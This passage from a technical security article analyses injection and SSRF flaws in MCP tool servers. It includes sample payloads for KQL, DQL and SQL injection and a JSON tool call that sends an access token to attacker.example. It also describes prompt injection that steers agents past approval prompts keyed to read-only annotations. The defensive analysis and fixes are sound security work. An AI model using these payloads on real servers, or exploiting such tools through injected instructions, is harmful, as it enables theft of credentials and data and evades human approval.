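Repeated decoding causes a similar problem. If the caller writes `%2F` as part of the ID, `quote` turns it into `%252F`. A proxy that decodes once produces `%2F`, and an application that decodes again produces a slash.

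The tool server's developer can't tell from its code whether the API treats an encoded slash as a path separator, but can test this by requesting a known resource with an encoded slash in its path. If `/users/42%2Fprofile` returns the same data as `/users/42/profile`, the tool server should refuse identifiers that contain slashes or percent signs. Refusing them for every API would break some tools, because some APIs use identifiers that contain a slash, such as a project addressed as `group%2Fproject`.

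### Building the path safely

A sound rule for the tool server is to encode each value as a single segment, reject `.` and `..`, and then compare the resolved path with the template. In Python, for templates in which each placeholder fills a whole segment:

```python
from urllib.parse import quote, urljoin

def safe_url(base, template, values):
    base = base.rstrip("/") + "/"
    parts = []
    for part in template.strip("/").split("/"):
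        if part.startswith("{"):
            part = quote(str(values[part[1:-1]]), safe="")
        if part in ("", ".", ".."):
            raise ValueError("invalid path segment")
        parts.append(part)
    expected = base + "/".join(parts)
    url = urljoin(base, "/".join(parts))
    if url != expected:
        raise ValueError("resolution changed the path")
    return url
```

The function also rejects empty values, because on many APIs a request with one would return the list of all users. It tests each segment after filling it in, which matters in code that allows several placeholders in one segment. In `{a}{b}`, for example, two values of `.` are each harmless but combine into `..`.

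Although the function has already refused the dots, the final comparison guards against mistakes in the earlier steps. It also catches a `..` in the base address, which the loop does not examine. If the HTTP client rewrites URLs, the comparison should use the address in the finished request.

Comparing the path with its template would not be enough without encoding the ID. For the template `/users/{id}`, the unencoded value `42?include=cards` produces the path `/users/42`, which matches the template, plus a query string requesting the customer's payment cards. Encoding prevents this by keeping the question mark inside the ID.

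An identifier that matches the name of a fixed endpoint passes every step. Many APIs have a fixed endpoint beside a variable one, such as `/users/export` beside `/users/{id}`, and OpenAPI gives the fixed path priority when both match. The call `get_user_profile(id="export")` then requests an export of all customers. It passes because `export` contains no special characters and the path has the right shape.

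If the OpenAPI description lists `/users/export`, the tool server can detect that the finished path matches that operation more closely than the tool's own and refuse the call. This fails for endpoints that the developer left out of the description, which are often the ones they most wanted to keep from agents. If customer IDs are always numbers, accepting only digits solves the problem and also excludes dots, slashes and percent signs. If IDs are usernames, the API's developers have to make sure that no endpoint name is also a valid username.

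## Names and filters inserted into a database query

A caller who breaks out of one segment of a URL path can choose a different endpoint. Many databases have only one endpoint for queries, and the text of the query determines what the database does. If a tool inserts a caller-supplied string into that text, the caller may be able to write part of the query. Vulnerability reports from 2025 and 2026 describe callers doing this through table names, time frames and database names, in one case despite a check on the query itself.

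### A table name that contains a query

Azure Data Explorer is a Microsoft service for analysing logs and other large datasets. In its query language, KQL, a query usually starts with a table, and each vertical bar passes the rows to another operation. `Orders | take 5` returns five rows from the table `Orders`. `Orders | getschema` returns the names and types of the table's columns instead of its rows.

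An open-source tool server called adx-mcp-server gives agents five tools for this service. One of them, `get_table_schema`, retrieves "schema information for a specified table", according to the description in the source code on Glama's *adx-mcp-server* page. Its only argument is a string, `table_name`, and it builds its query with this line of Python:

```python
query = f"{table_name} | getschema"
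```

Python replaces the braces and their contents with the argument, so `Orders` produces `Orders | getschema`. The advisory for the flaw, OSV's *GHSA-vphc-468g-8rfp* (2026), demonstrates it with this table name:

```
sensitive_data | project Secret, Password | take 100 //
```

The server then sends this query:

```
sensitive_data | project Secret, Password | take 100 // | getschema
```

`project` keeps only the two named columns, and `take` returns up to 100 rows. KQL ignores everything from `//` to the end of the line, so `getschema` never runs. The server converts whatever rows the query returns into a list, so the agent receives passwords from a tool for looking up column names.

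Python joins the two pieces of text into a single string before the database receives it. The string doesn't show which characters came from the developer, so a vertical bar starts a new operation no matter who wrote it.

Two other tools on the server, `sample_table_data` and `get_table_details`, insert table names the same way. The injection matters less in `sample_table_data`, because that tool is meant to return random rows from any table the caller names. A caller can get passwords by naming the `sensitive_data` table, which is within the tool's declared scope.

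The flaw in `get_table_schema` matters most when an operator has restricted the other tools. The package's PyPI page, *Azure Data Explorer MCP Server*, explains that operators can choose which tools to offer. An operator who offers only `list_tables` and `get_table_schema` would expect an agent to see how the database is organised but not read any rows. OSV makes a similar point about clients that run "safe" tools automatically but ask for confirmation before `execute_query`, the server's raw-query tool.

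The credential may also have more permissions than the operator realises. The instructions on PyPI tell users to log in to Azure from the command line with an account that can access the database, so on a developer's laptop the service credential may be the developer's own account, with all its permissions.

A reviewer who reads only the listing will probably miss the flaw. PolicyLayer, which sells a gateway for agents, rates the tool "Low Risk" in *get_table_schema* because an attacker "cannot access, modify, or delete data through this tool alone". It recommends allowing the tool with no condition on the argument. The rating is reasonable given the description, but it is wrong for the vulnerable code.

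A fix exists, but as of mid-July 2026 the databases listed no packaged release with it. NVD's *CVE-2026-33980 Detail* (2026) identifies source code commit `0abe0ee` as the patch. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2327* (2026), published on 13 July, gives 1.1.0 as the last affected release and lists no fixed one. GitLab's *CVE-2026-33980* (2026) links to the patch but lists no solution. Operators should therefore run the server from source code that includes the commit.

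NVD's text also lists the affected versions as up to 0.1.1, probably a mistake for 1.1.0. Someone running version 1.0.5 who checked only NVD would wrongly conclude they were safe.

### Time frames and cluster identifiers

Dynatrace makes software for monitoring computer systems, and its query language, DQL, is also a pipeline. In July 2026, Dynatrace disclosed that several tools on its MCP server pasted arguments into DQL queries. Corgea's *@dynatrace-oss/dynatrace-mcp-server has a DQL injection via parameters not documented as DQL* reproduces the text of the advisory.

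| Argument | What a reader would expect it to contain | What a caller could change |
|---|---|---|
| `timeframe` | A period such as `24h` | The time window and the operations after it |
| `clusterId` | The identifier of one Kubernetes cluster, a group of machines that run software together | The filter that selects the cluster's events |
| `entityNames` | The names of monitored services or machines | The fields that the tool returns |

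For an ordinary cluster ID such as `abc-123`, with the second identifier left empty, the filter looks like this:

```
| filter k8s.cluster.uid == "abc-123" or dt.entity.kubernetes_cluster == ""
```

If the caller supplies `x" or 1==1 //` as the ID, the server builds this filter instead:

```
| filter k8s.cluster.uid == "x" or 1==1 //" or dt.entity.kubernetes_cluster == ""
```

The quotation mark after `x` ends the text that the developer meant to compare. The condition `1==1` is true for every event, and the comment removes the rest of the line, so the tool returns events from all clusters.

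The example for `entityNames` also closes a quotation mark, then replaces the tool's list of fields, `id, name, type`, with `id, name, tags`. The `timeframe` argument has no quotation marks around it, so a caller can write a time period, finish the time window and add another operation.

The advisory's example for `timeframe` adds a field called `internal_secret` and ends with `//`. This comment removes only the rest of that line, although Corgea describes it as removing the rest of the query. The filter on the next line still runs. Whether the caller receives the extra field depends on the lines after that.

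These queries still begin with the data source that the developer chose. But DQL has commands such as `append`, which adds the results of a second query, so a caller who can add operations can also bring in data from any other source that the credential can read.

All the affected tools have the annotation `readOnlyHint: true`, which remains accurate because the injected queries in the advisory only read data. But the annotation doesn't specify which data a tool reads, and a client that skips confirmation because of it will also skip confirmation for the altered query. The server's raw-query tool, `execute_dql`, can already run any DQL with the same token. The advisory's severity score is 4.3, compared with 8.3 for the Azure flaw. GitLab's *GHSA-pqh8-p93p-2rx7* (2026) lists version 2.1.1 as the fix.

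The schemas for these arguments accepted any string. For two of the arguments, a stricter pattern would have stopped the attack. A time frame can be limited to a few digits followed by `m`, `h` or `d`, and a cluster ID to letters, digits and hyphens. (The time frame pattern would still accept `999d`, so a tool with a maximum period also has to check the number.) Service names are harder to restrict because a legitimate name may contain punctuation.

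### Two guards that callers could get around

Some tools let the model write the whole query and rely on the server to refuse dangerous ones. The declared scope is then the set of queries the server is supposed to allow. In two database servers, callers could bypass the guard without finding a dangerous query that it misclassified as safe.

The first is the MCP server for Apache Doris, a database for analysing large amounts of data. It authenticates each user, assigns a clearance level from public to secret, and validates queries before running them. Akamai, a network security company, found a gap in this validation while reviewing official MCP servers. The server's `exec_query` function takes a query and, among other arguments, a database name (`db_name`). The server validated the query but not the name, then put the name in front of the query.

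Akamai's finding is easier to follow with an invented example. If the server selects a database with a `USE` statement, the name `sales` and the query `SELECT 1` produce `USE sales; SELECT 1`. With the name `sales; SELECT * FROM hr.salaries`, the result is:

```sql
USE sales; SELECT * FROM hr.salaries; SELECT 1
```

The validator approved `SELECT 1`, but the database received three statements, including one that reads salaries.

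Running the same validator on the combined text would not have solved the problem. Akamai also found that it checked only the first portion of a query and disregarded the rest. In the example above, it might have approved `USE sales` and stopped. The check has to cover all the text that the server is about to send. (Google's MCP Toolbox made a related mistake with URLs, which it checked before resolving the path.)

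Apache issued a patch on 30 December 2025. Its public notice of April 2026, on a mailing list hosted by Openwall (2026), lists 0.6.1 as the first unaffected version. That version also fixes a second flaw, which Apache announced on the same list in June (Openwall, 2026). In this second case, the server inserted a database name into a query for metadata, such as table names, and ran it without passing on the caller's authorisation context. Validating user queries did not prevent this, because the server built the metadata query in another part of its code.

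The second is Anthropic's reference server for the database PostgreSQL, which accepted any SQL query but was supposed to prevent changes. According to Datadog Security Labs' *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025), the server started a read-only transaction for every call, ran the caller's SQL and then rolled the transaction back. PostgreSQL blocks changes to tables inside a read-only transaction, so a command to delete tables failed if sent on its own.

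However, the server's database library accepted several statements in one string, and SQL includes a statement that ends a transaction. If a caller sends `COMMIT; UPDATE customers SET plan = 'free';`, PostgreSQL runs this sequence:

| Statement | Written by | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| `BEGIN TRANSACTION READ ONLY` | Tool server | PostgreSQL starts refusing changes |
| `COMMIT` | Caller | The read-only transaction ends |
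| `UPDATE customers SET plan = 'free'` | Caller | Every customer's plan changes |
| `ROLLBACK` | Tool server | PostgreSQL warns that no transaction is in progress |

Datadog's own demonstration deleted all the tables. The tool accepted raw queries, but its reach was still excessive because its listing offered only read-only queries.

Datadog's patch runs the caller's SQL as a prepared statement, which PostgreSQL limits to a single statement. A caller can still send `COMMIT`, but nothing can follow it in the same call. The patch also closes the database connection after each call, so altered settings can't carry over to the next call.

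Anthropic fixed the source code on 29 May 2025 and archived the server the same day, but did not publish the fix in the npm package that most people install. Datadog found that the vulnerable package still had about 21,000 downloads a week that August. Zed Industries, which makes a code editor, maintains a separate version with the fix.

### Bound parameters

The usual remedy for values is a bound parameter. The developer writes a query with a placeholder and sends the value separately:

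```sql
SELECT name, plan FROM customers WHERE id = ?
```

OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet* explains that the database can then distinguish code from data, whatever the caller writes. If the caller supplies `42 OR 1=1`, the database treats the whole string as a customer ID and does not run the `OR`.

KQL has the same feature, which Microsoft recommends for queries that include user input. A filter on cluster IDs could look like this:

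```
declare query_parameters(cluster:string);
Events | where ClusterId == cluster
```

The value `x" or 1==1 //` would match only a cluster with exactly that name.

Without bound parameters, a developer has to escape special characters, which OWASP strongly discourages because it is fragile. In many languages, a backslash before a quotation mark makes the mark part of the text. But if the code adds a backslash before each quotation mark and leaves existing backslashes alone, it turns a caller's `\"` into `\\"`, which is an escaped backslash followed by a quotation mark that ends the text.

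A bound value can still do more than the developer expected if the query gives it a special meaning. In `WHERE name LIKE ?`, for example, the value `%` matches every customer who has a name, because `LIKE` treats the percent sign as a wildcard. Binding also doesn't help when the caller supplies the whole query, as with the PostgreSQL server, because there is no fixed query text to keep the caller's input separate from.

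Placeholders usually can't stand for table or column names, which is the more important limit for `get_table_schema`. The database needs those names to interpret the query before it fills in any values. OWASP also lists sort order among the parts of a query where placeholders don't work.

KQL offers a partial workaround. Microsoft's *table()* describes a function that accepts a table's name as a string if the string is constant when the query calls the function. A query parameter should meet that condition, so the tool could use `table(name) | getschema` and bind `name`. But if no table has the given name and a stored function does, `table()` runs the function. This workaround also doesn't help with `get_table_details`, which puts the name into a management command.

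Some names can be kept out of the query text. The Azure server passes its configured database to the client library as a separate argument. The Doris server could similarly check that the caller may use a database, then select it when connecting, so that it wouldn't need to add anything before the query.

### Looking up names

When a table name has to go into the text, the server can compare it with a list of known tables. The Azure server already has a tool, `list_tables`, that retrieves such a list. A safer version of the query builder would be:

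```python
def schema_query(table_name, known_tables):
    if table_name not in known_tables:
        raise ValueError("unknown table")
    return f"['{table_name}'] | getschema"
```

The brackets and quotation marks let a KQL query refer to names that contain spaces or hyphens. They can't replace the lookup, because a caller could close the quotation mark, as in the Dynatrace example.

Checking a name's characters is simpler than checking the name against a list of tables, but weaker. According to Microsoft's *entity names*, KQL names may contain letters, digits, underscores, spaces, dots and dashes. A server that rejected all other characters would stop OSV's example, which contains vertical bars and slashes. But it would still accept the names of stored functions, which a list of tables excludes.

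A lookup confirms that a table exists, but it doesn't check whether the agent should have access to it. If `known_tables` contains every table the credential can access, it includes `sensitive_data`. That may be acceptable for `get_table_schema`, which now returns only column names. But `sample_table_data` would still return the passwords, so the operator would need a shorter list for that tool.

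OWASP goes further and treats letting users choose table names as a symptom of poor design that may justify a full rewrite. This seems right for a shop's website, where the developer knows which table each page needs. But choosing the table is the main function of a tool for exploring a database. OWASP's fallback, which maps each accepted argument to a table name written in the code, suits a server with a small, stable set of tables.

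### Read-only database roles

A database role is an account with its own permissions. The database enforces those permissions when it runs a query, so the protection doesn't depend on another program interpreting the query text correctly.

Akamai found that the MCP server for Apache Pinot, another analytics database, checked only that a query began with `SELECT`, which let callers read any table. On PostgreSQL, the same check wouldn't even guarantee that a query only reads, because a `SELECT` can call a function that changes data.

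With a suitable role, an operator can limit both the action and the tables. In PostgreSQL:

```sql
CREATE ROLE agent_reader LOGIN;
GRANT SELECT ON customers, orders TO agent_reader;
```

If Anthropic's server had connected with this role, a caller could still have ended the read-only transaction. The `UPDATE` would then have failed, because the role has no permission to change `customers`.

The account's permissions have to enforce the restriction. PostgreSQL's `default_transaction_read_only` setting only makes an account's transactions read-only by default. A session can switch it off, so a caller who can run several statements could get around it much as they got around the read-only transaction.

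Datadog Security Labs recommend a restricted account but describe an attack that it doesn't stop. The PostgreSQL server reused database connections, and any account can change some settings of its own connection. An attacker could set the time limit for statements to one millisecond, and later queries on that connection would fail, including other users' queries. Even a role that can only read tables may be able to change data by calling a stored function, because some of these functions run with their owner's permissions.

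The larger limitation is that a read-only role still allows reading, which causes much of the harm in these cases. In the Azure example, a query run under a read-only role with access to `sensitive_data` would still have returned the passwords. To prevent that, the operator has to deny access to the table or columns. OWASP suggests creating a view, which presents selected parts of a table as if they were a separate table, and giving the account access only to the view.

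A single database role for the whole server has the same weakness as a shared API key. Separate roles for tools with different purposes would reduce this weakness, but the server would then have to manage several credentials.

### Fixed GraphQL operations

A developer can also write the entire query in advance and let the model supply only values. Apollo MCP Server does this for GraphQL, a query language in which a client lists the fields it wants and the API checks the request against a typed schema. Each tool is normally one stored operation, such as this invented one:

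```graphql
query GetUserProfile($id: ID!) {
  user(id: $id) {
    name
    plan
  }
}
```

The model supplies `id`, which is sent as a variable, separately from the query. If the model writes `42") { invoices }`, the API looks for a user whose ID is that whole string. The text can't add `invoices` to the list of fields, because the API doesn't parse the variable as part of the query.

Bound parameters provide the same separation, and a fixed SQL query could be just as safe. GraphQL adds a short, typed document that lists the fields the tool can return. An administrator can compare this document with the tool's description without working out how the server assembles a string.

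The protection depends on narrow variables. An operation might accept a filter object that lets the caller combine many conditions, or a search string with its own operators, as the invented `search_tickets` tool does. If the API's code pastes the `id` into an SQL query, the original flaw reappears in the code behind GraphQL.

*Where Apollo MCP Server Stands on the OWASP MCP Top 10* (Lawrence, 2026), an audit by the server's own developers, describes further limits. An attacker can still steer an agent into calling a permitted operation for a harmful purpose. The server also has an optional `execute` tool, which runs operations that the model writes itself. The server checks these operations against the schema, but only confirms that their fields and types are valid, so enabling `execute` brings back a raw-query tool.

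The server's `mutation_mode` setting controls which operations that change data, called mutations in GraphQL, are available. By default, the server offers none. The value `explicit` allows only mutations that a developer has stored in advance, and `all` also lets `execute` run any valid mutation. Lawrence points out that these settings apply when the server is configured and don't require a person to approve each call. Someone with access to a hosted collection of operations can also change what a tool does, and the server picks up the change within about a minute without an approval step.

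Fixed operations suit tasks that developers can anticipate, such as looking up a customer's plan, but work poorly when an analyst wants an agent to explore an unfamiliar database. Datadog Security Labs notes that agents often need more open-ended tools than conventional applications do. For such exploration, I would rather have an openly listed raw-query tool with a narrow read-only role than several supposedly safe tools that paste names into queries.

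## Arguments that choose the destination or its settings

In the path and query flaws, the tool server still sends its request to the service the credential belongs to. For example, a workflow ID of `../executions` reaches the wrong n8n endpoint, but the credential goes only to n8n. Some tools also let the caller choose the host or change how the request travels, so the caller can send the credential to a machine they control.

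A request to an attacker's machine is not an upstream operation, so it does not extend the tool's reach as defined here. The harm comes afterwards, when the attacker uses the key without the tool.

### Contentful's export and import tools

Contentful sells a content management system in which customers keep articles, images and other material in containers called spaces. Its MCP server has a tool named `export_space`, with the description "Export entire space to file" in the listing on PolicyLayer's *export_space* page, and a matching `import_space`. Hatagale (2026), in *CVE-2026-53957*, reports that both tools also accepted four arguments about the connection:

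| Argument | Effect |
|---|---|
| `host` | Replaces Contentful's API host in the address of each request |
| `insecure` | Switches from encrypted HTTPS to plain HTTP |
| `proxy` | Sends the requests through an intermediary that the caller names |
| `rawProxy` | Passes the proxy settings straight to the HTTP client, skipping the usual HTTPS setup |

Arguments like these are enough for an attack:

```json
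{
  "spaceId": "abc123",
  "host": "attacker.example",
  "insecure": true
}
```

The library behind the tool builds an address that begins with `http://attacker.example/spaces/` and attaches the server's access token to the request. The export will probably fail because the attacker's machine holds no Contentful data, but the attacker will already have the token.

An attacker can also leave `host` alone and set the proxy. The request is still addressed to Contentful, so it would pass a check on the host. `insecure` matters more here than when the attacker changes `host`. Attackers can easily get a valid certificate for their own domain but not for Contentful's, so a proxy normally can't read the HTTPS data it relays.

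Contentful offers a hosted server, where each user signs in, and a local one that uses a personal access token. According to Contentful's *Model Context Protocol (MCP) server*, every call on the local server runs as the token's owner, limited only by the token's permissions.

The export and import tools are off by default, but Hatagale's demonstration begins by turning them on with another tool call. The attacker doesn't need direct access to the server, since any Contentful entry that the model reads can contain the instructions. PolicyLayer recommends limiting how often an agent calls `export_space`, but that would not help here because a single call leaks the token.

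The schema listed all four arguments, so an administrator who read it closely could have noticed `host`, but would probably have taken it as a way to choose among Contentful's own servers. Nothing in "Export entire space to file" suggests that the tool will send the server's token to any machine the caller names.

### Copying every argument into the options

The export library takes a single options object, which the tool server built with JavaScript's spread syntax. In simplified form:

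```js
const options = { ...args, managementToken: token };
```

`...args` copies every field of the caller's arguments into the new object. If two fields have the same name, the later one overwrites the earlier one. The caller couldn't replace the token because it comes after the spread. But the server never set `host`, so the caller's value remained.

The server's other tools didn't have this flaw. They used a helper function that always takes the host from the server's configuration, while the export and import tools used one that supplied only the token.

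This kind of options object mixes task details, such as which space to export, with connection settings. The library's developers can reasonably assume that a programmer chose both. A spread lets the caller set any option that gets through the schema, including ones the programmer never considered.

Contentful's patch removes the four named fields before copying the rest. This stops the published attacks, but the developers must remember to extend the list whenever they add another connection setting to the schema. Zod, the server's validation library, gives some protection by dropping undeclared fields by default. A server that accepts undeclared fields lacks this protection, so an upgrade of the export library could add a dangerous option without any change to the tool.

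A fixed list of accepted fields removes the problem:

```js
const options = {
  spaceId: args.spaceId,
  environmentId: args.environmentId,
  managementToken: token,
  host: config.host
};
```

If the caller supplies `proxy`, the server doesn't copy it. A new library option has no effect until a developer adds a line for it, which a reviewer can see. This makes the code somewhat repetitive for tools with many arguments. The list restricts only which fields the caller can set, so the server still has to check their values, for example if the library puts `environmentId` into a URL path.

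### Redirects and address headers in n8n-mcp

The Contentful flaw is a server-side request forgery (SSRF). An attacker can use such a flaw to steal the service credential, or to reach machines that accept connections from the tool server but not from the attacker. For instance, cloud providers run a metadata service at `169.254.169.254` that can give programs on a virtual machine temporary credentials for the company's cloud account. If a tool fetches that address and returns the response, the caller gets those credentials.

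n8n-mcp had a check that was supposed to block such addresses. GitLab's *GHSA-8g7g-hmwm-6rv2* describes how callers got around it with a redirect, an ordinary HTTP response that tells the client to fetch a different URL:

1. The caller gives a tool the URL of a webhook, an address that starts a workflow.
2. n8n-mcp checks the URL, which points to a permitted public host.
3. That host answers with a redirect to a forbidden address.
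4. The HTTP client follows the redirect automatically, without another check, and n8n-mcp returns the response to the caller.

Version 2.50.1 stopped following redirects for these requests, according to Aikido (2026), a security company.

The next release fixed CVE-2026-44694, which involved addresses in HTTP headers as well as in tool arguments. A company can host one copy of n8n-mcp for many customers, each with their own n8n installation. Glama's *Flexible Instance Configuration* explains that the caller then sends the installation's address in one header, `X-N8n-Url`, and its key in another. Corgea's *n8n-mcp webhook and API client paths has an authenticated SSRF* reports that a customer could use the address header to reach the hosting company's internal services and cloud credentials. Prompt injection could reach the same services through tool arguments, even on a server on the user's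 machine.

Callers who send both the address and the n8n key only get their own key back if they redirect the request, and the advisory for CVE-2026-44694 doesn't describe a key leak. The key is at risk when one party supplies it and another chooses the address. OSV's *GHSA-56c3-vfp2-5qqj* (2026) covers an earlier flaw in applications that embed n8n-mcp, where the key was sent to the chosen host. If such an application supplies the key but takes the address from a user, the user can collect the key.

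Counting these, the databases published four flaws in how n8n-mcp checks addresses between 8 April and 8 May 2026:

| Fixed in | What the caller could use |
|---|---|
| 2.47.4 | Any URL in the address header |
| 2.47.14 | A forbidden IPv4 address written in IPv6 form, such as `[::ffff:169.254.169.254]` |
| 2.50.1 | A permitted URL that redirects to a forbidden one |
| 2.50.2 | An n8n address, which the check on webhook URLs did not cover |

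GitLab's *CVE-2026-39974* (2026) describes the flaw in the first row. Its fix added the check that the IPv6 form later evaded. This suggests that recognising every forbidden destination is much harder than recognising the one correct one. A list of forbidden addresses can also block legitimate ones. After 2.50.2, operators who run n8n on the same machine as n8n-mcp have to loosen the check, because it treats their installation as an internal service. A filter for internal addresses would not have protected Contentful's token, since an attacker's machine is usually on the public internet.

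GitLab's *CVE-2026-44694* (2026) also classifies that flaw as a race between check and use. Wiz's *CVE-2026-53708* describes a similar race in IBM's MCP gateway, which attackers could exploit through the domain name system. An attacker who controls a domain can return a harmless address when the gateway checks the name, then an internal address when the gateway looks it up again to connect. The fix is to connect to the address that passed the check. n8n-mcp adopted a version of this fix and refined it further in release 2.71.0, according to NewReleases' *github czlonkowski/n8n-mcp v2.71.0*.

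### The GitLab server's dynamic API address

A header doesn't appear in a tool's listing, and the code that reads it may be separate from the tool's code. GitLab's *CVE-2026-27826* (2026) makes this point about a server for Atlassian's products, which took the addresses of two services from headers, a flaw that an analysis of the individual tools would not have found.

A popular community-made server for the code-hosting platform GitLab had a similar feature. (GitLab publishes the vulnerability entries but did not make this server.) When an operator turns on `ENABLE_DYNAMIC_API_URL`, the server sends its API calls to whatever address the caller puts in the `X-GitLab-API-URL` header. This lets one server work with several GitLab installations. Pluto Security's *How We Made a GitLab MCP Server Hand Us Its Own Access Token* reports that the server checked only whether the value was a well-formed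 URL, then sent the request there with a GitLab token attached.

Pluto Security says the stolen token is the server's own, and the advisory rates the flaw 9.6 out of 10. The server's documentation, Glama's *Dynamic GitLab API URL Support*, suggests a narrower danger, because the setting is off by default and requires a mode in which callers send their own GitLab tokens. In that mode, an attacker who changes the address of their own request should receive only the token they sent. To get someone else's, they would have to put the header into that person's requests, perhaps through a shared configuration file. The high rating fits better if the server also holds its own token and uses it for callers' requests. Either way, the attacker can still use the server to contact internal machines.

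Pluto Security found an unrelated flaw in the same server. In its older SSE network mode, which the project's Docker setup used, the server required no login. Anyone who could reach it could use a file-upload tool to read the token from the server's environment. Adding a login closes that route but does not fix the address header, because a caller who has logged in can still send it. The two flaws also can't occur in the same configuration because, according to mcp-gitlab's *Environment Variables Reference*, the mode that dynamic addresses require cannot run together with SSE.

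Version 2.1.27, released on 22 June 2026, fixed both flaws with separate changes. For the header, the server now checks the host against a list that the operator sets. In the code that Pluto Security shows, this check covers only the hostname, so if `gitlab.company.com` were on the list, the server would accept `http://gitlab.company.com:9099` and send the token unencrypted to a different port. The check should also cover the scheme and port.

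### Keeping a credential with its host

The most effective remedy is to set the destination in the server's configuration and ignore any address from the caller. According to OSV, the flaw in embedded copies of n8n-mcp is unreachable if the application takes the address only from its own configuration. The hosted version of another GitLab server, documented on pkg.go.dev, always connects to `gitlab.com` and ignores the caller's address header. A service with many customers can store each customer's address and key together and choose the pair based on who has logged in.

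Configuration settings also need checking. *CVE-2026-81101* (2026), an entry from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, describes a program with two ways to set its API address. One accepted only the vendor's hosts, but the other, a `configure` command, accepted any URL and stored it beside the user's access token. An attacker who persuaded a user to run the command with an address the attacker controlled would receive the token.

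The next precaution is to recheck the destination after every redirect, or to refuse all redirects. Refusing is simpler, but some APIs redirect file downloads to a separate storage host. The tool server then has to permit that host too, without sending it the API's key.

Attaching the credential only to requests for the host it was issued for solves this. HTTP clients often remove the `Authorization` header when a redirect leads to another host, but they may keep custom headers that contain keys. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-53840* (2026) describes such a leak in OpenClaw, an AI agent that connects to MCP servers. A malicious server could redirect OpenClaw's request to another host and receive the secret headers the operator had configured.

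In Python, with the HTTP library httpx, a function for read requests could combine the three measures like this:

```python
import httpx

API = ("https", "api.example.com", None)
FILES = ("https", "files.example.com", None)

def fetch(client, url, token):
    url = httpx.URL(url)
    for _ in range(5):
        origin = (url.scheme, url.host, url.port)
        if origin not in (API, FILES):
            raise ValueError("destination not allowed")
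        headers = {}
        if origin == API:
            headers["Authorization"] = f"Bearer {token}"
        response = client.get(url, headers=headers, follow_redirects=False)
        if not response.has_redirect_location:
            return response
        url = url.join(response.headers["location"])
    raise ValueError("too many redirects")
```

The two permitted destinations are constants, and `None` stands for the default port. The loop checks each address before contacting it and adds the token only for the API. The `client` must not have a key in its default headers, because httpx would send that key to the storage host too. The function doesn't restrict the path, so a redirect within the API's host can still lead to a different endpoint.

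Binding the key to its host does not replace the check on destinations. A cloud metadata service may give out credentials without receiving a key, so a request without one can still do damage. Limits on outgoing network traffic can provide a second barrier against such requests.

Upgrading the tool server doesn't stop an attacker from using a leaked token directly. If a GitLab server ran with dynamic addresses turned on, Pluto Security advises its operator to revoke the token and issue a new one with the narrowest permissions that work. The same precaution makes sense for a Contentful token if an agent could call the vulnerable export or import tools.

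## When exceeding a tool's declared scope is a security breach

Sending a service's key to an attacker is a security breach. It is harder to judge a tool that exceeds its declared scope when the tool server sends the request to the right service, with a valid key, and the service accepts it. Two 2026 advisories, one for the Azure Data Explorer server and one for Dynatrace's, describe nearly the same flaw but differ on how serious it is. Much of the difference comes from whether a tool's declared scope counts as a security boundary.

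### The argument from approval

The case for a boundary runs as follows:

1. People and client programs grant permission one tool at a time.
2. They rely on the tool's name, description and annotations to do so.
3. A crafted argument can make an approved tool perform an operation that nobody approved.
4. The declared scope is therefore a security boundary, and a call that crosses it is a breach.

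Claude's settings illustrate the first premise. Each write or delete tool in a connector (a tool server added to Claude) can be set to "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked". Anthropic tells administrators that blocking these tools keeps the connector read-only, which is true only if none of the remaining tools can write. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Developer mode* explains that a user can have ChatGPT remember an approval for one tool for the rest of a conversation. A user who does this when approving `get_table_schema` for the table `Orders` may also have approved later calls in which the table name contains a query.

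The vulnerabilities described so far establish the third premise, but the conclusion doesn't quite follow, because people rely on many things that aren't security boundaries, such as file names. The argument also requires that some control would have stopped or flagged the operation if the agent had requested it openly.

Whether a crafted argument breaches security depends on what would have happened if the agent had called the tool meant for that operation. If a control would have refused the call, the attacker has bypassed an access restriction, as in n8n-mcp, where a workflow ID could reach the endpoint of a disabled tool. If a person would have had to approve the call, the attacker has bypassed that approval. If the call would have run anyway, the tool has a bug, but the attacker has gained no access that the operator was withholding.

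### Clients that approve tools by annotation

Several clients skip the confirmation prompt when a tool is annotated as read-only. According to Anthropic's criteria for its connector directory, Claude uses annotations to set automatic permissions, so read-only tools can run without confirmation for each call, while destructive tools always require it. Anthropic's *What is MCP?* attributes 30% of directory rejections to missing annotations.

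The criteria also require a tool's description to match its behaviour. But by default, Anthropic lists a connector after an automatic scan. Reviewers test each tool only if Anthropic has selected its connector for a "Verified" label, and even then they could miss a fault that appears only with a crafted argument.

ChatGPT's developer mode follows `readOnlyHint` and treats a tool without it as a write action, which needs confirmation by default. Some users also have an "Allow read actions" setting. OpenAI says that under this setting, ChatGPT reads from an app without asking but asks before making changes.

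OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, gained a similar "writes" mode in July 2026. *The Writes Mode* (Vaughan, 2026) reports that in this mode, tools annotated as read-only run without approval, and all others require it. If a tool is annotated as both read-only and destructive, OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* specifies that Codex must ask for approval. This rule handles contradictory annotations, but it doesn't help when a read-only annotation made in good faith is wrong for a particular text argument.

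Other clients are more careful. VS Code's *Integrate MCP servers with Copilot* warns developers not to assume that `readOnlyHint` bypasses approval, though the hint still affects the default confirmation in an older mode due for removal in February 2027. By default, Google's command-line agent, Gemini CLI, asks for approval before running read-only MCP tools in planning mode, but its documentation includes a short rule that approves them automatically for every server.

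These behaviours can change, so an operator can't safely assume that today's permission prompt will still appear next month. In the forum post *Custom Internal App (MCP Server) Started Requesting Permission*, a developer complains that ChatGPT began asking permission to run read-only tools that used to run without a prompt.

Google Cloud's *Prevent read-write MCP tool use* describes an access control policy that blocks any tool whose `tool.isReadOnly` attribute isn't true, across a project, folder or organisation. If a crafted argument makes a tool with that attribute set to true write data, the policy won't stop the call.

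### Two severity scores for similar flaws

Both servers pasted arguments from narrow lookup tools into queries, and both also had a raw-query tool. The Azure advisory on OSV rates the flaw's severity 8.3 out of 10. `execute_query` accepts any query by design, but some clients ask for confirmation only before running that tool, so the advisory concludes that the injection "bypasses this trust boundary".

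Dynatrace judges the same arrangement less severely. According to the advisory text that Corgea reproduces, the operator's token already gives `execute_dql` full query access, so the injection doesn't expose any additional data. The stated harm is "the auto-approval pathway and the broken tool contract, not privilege escalation", and the severity is 4.3. The contract here means the limits built into each tool, such as which fields it returns, how far back it searches and how many results it displays.

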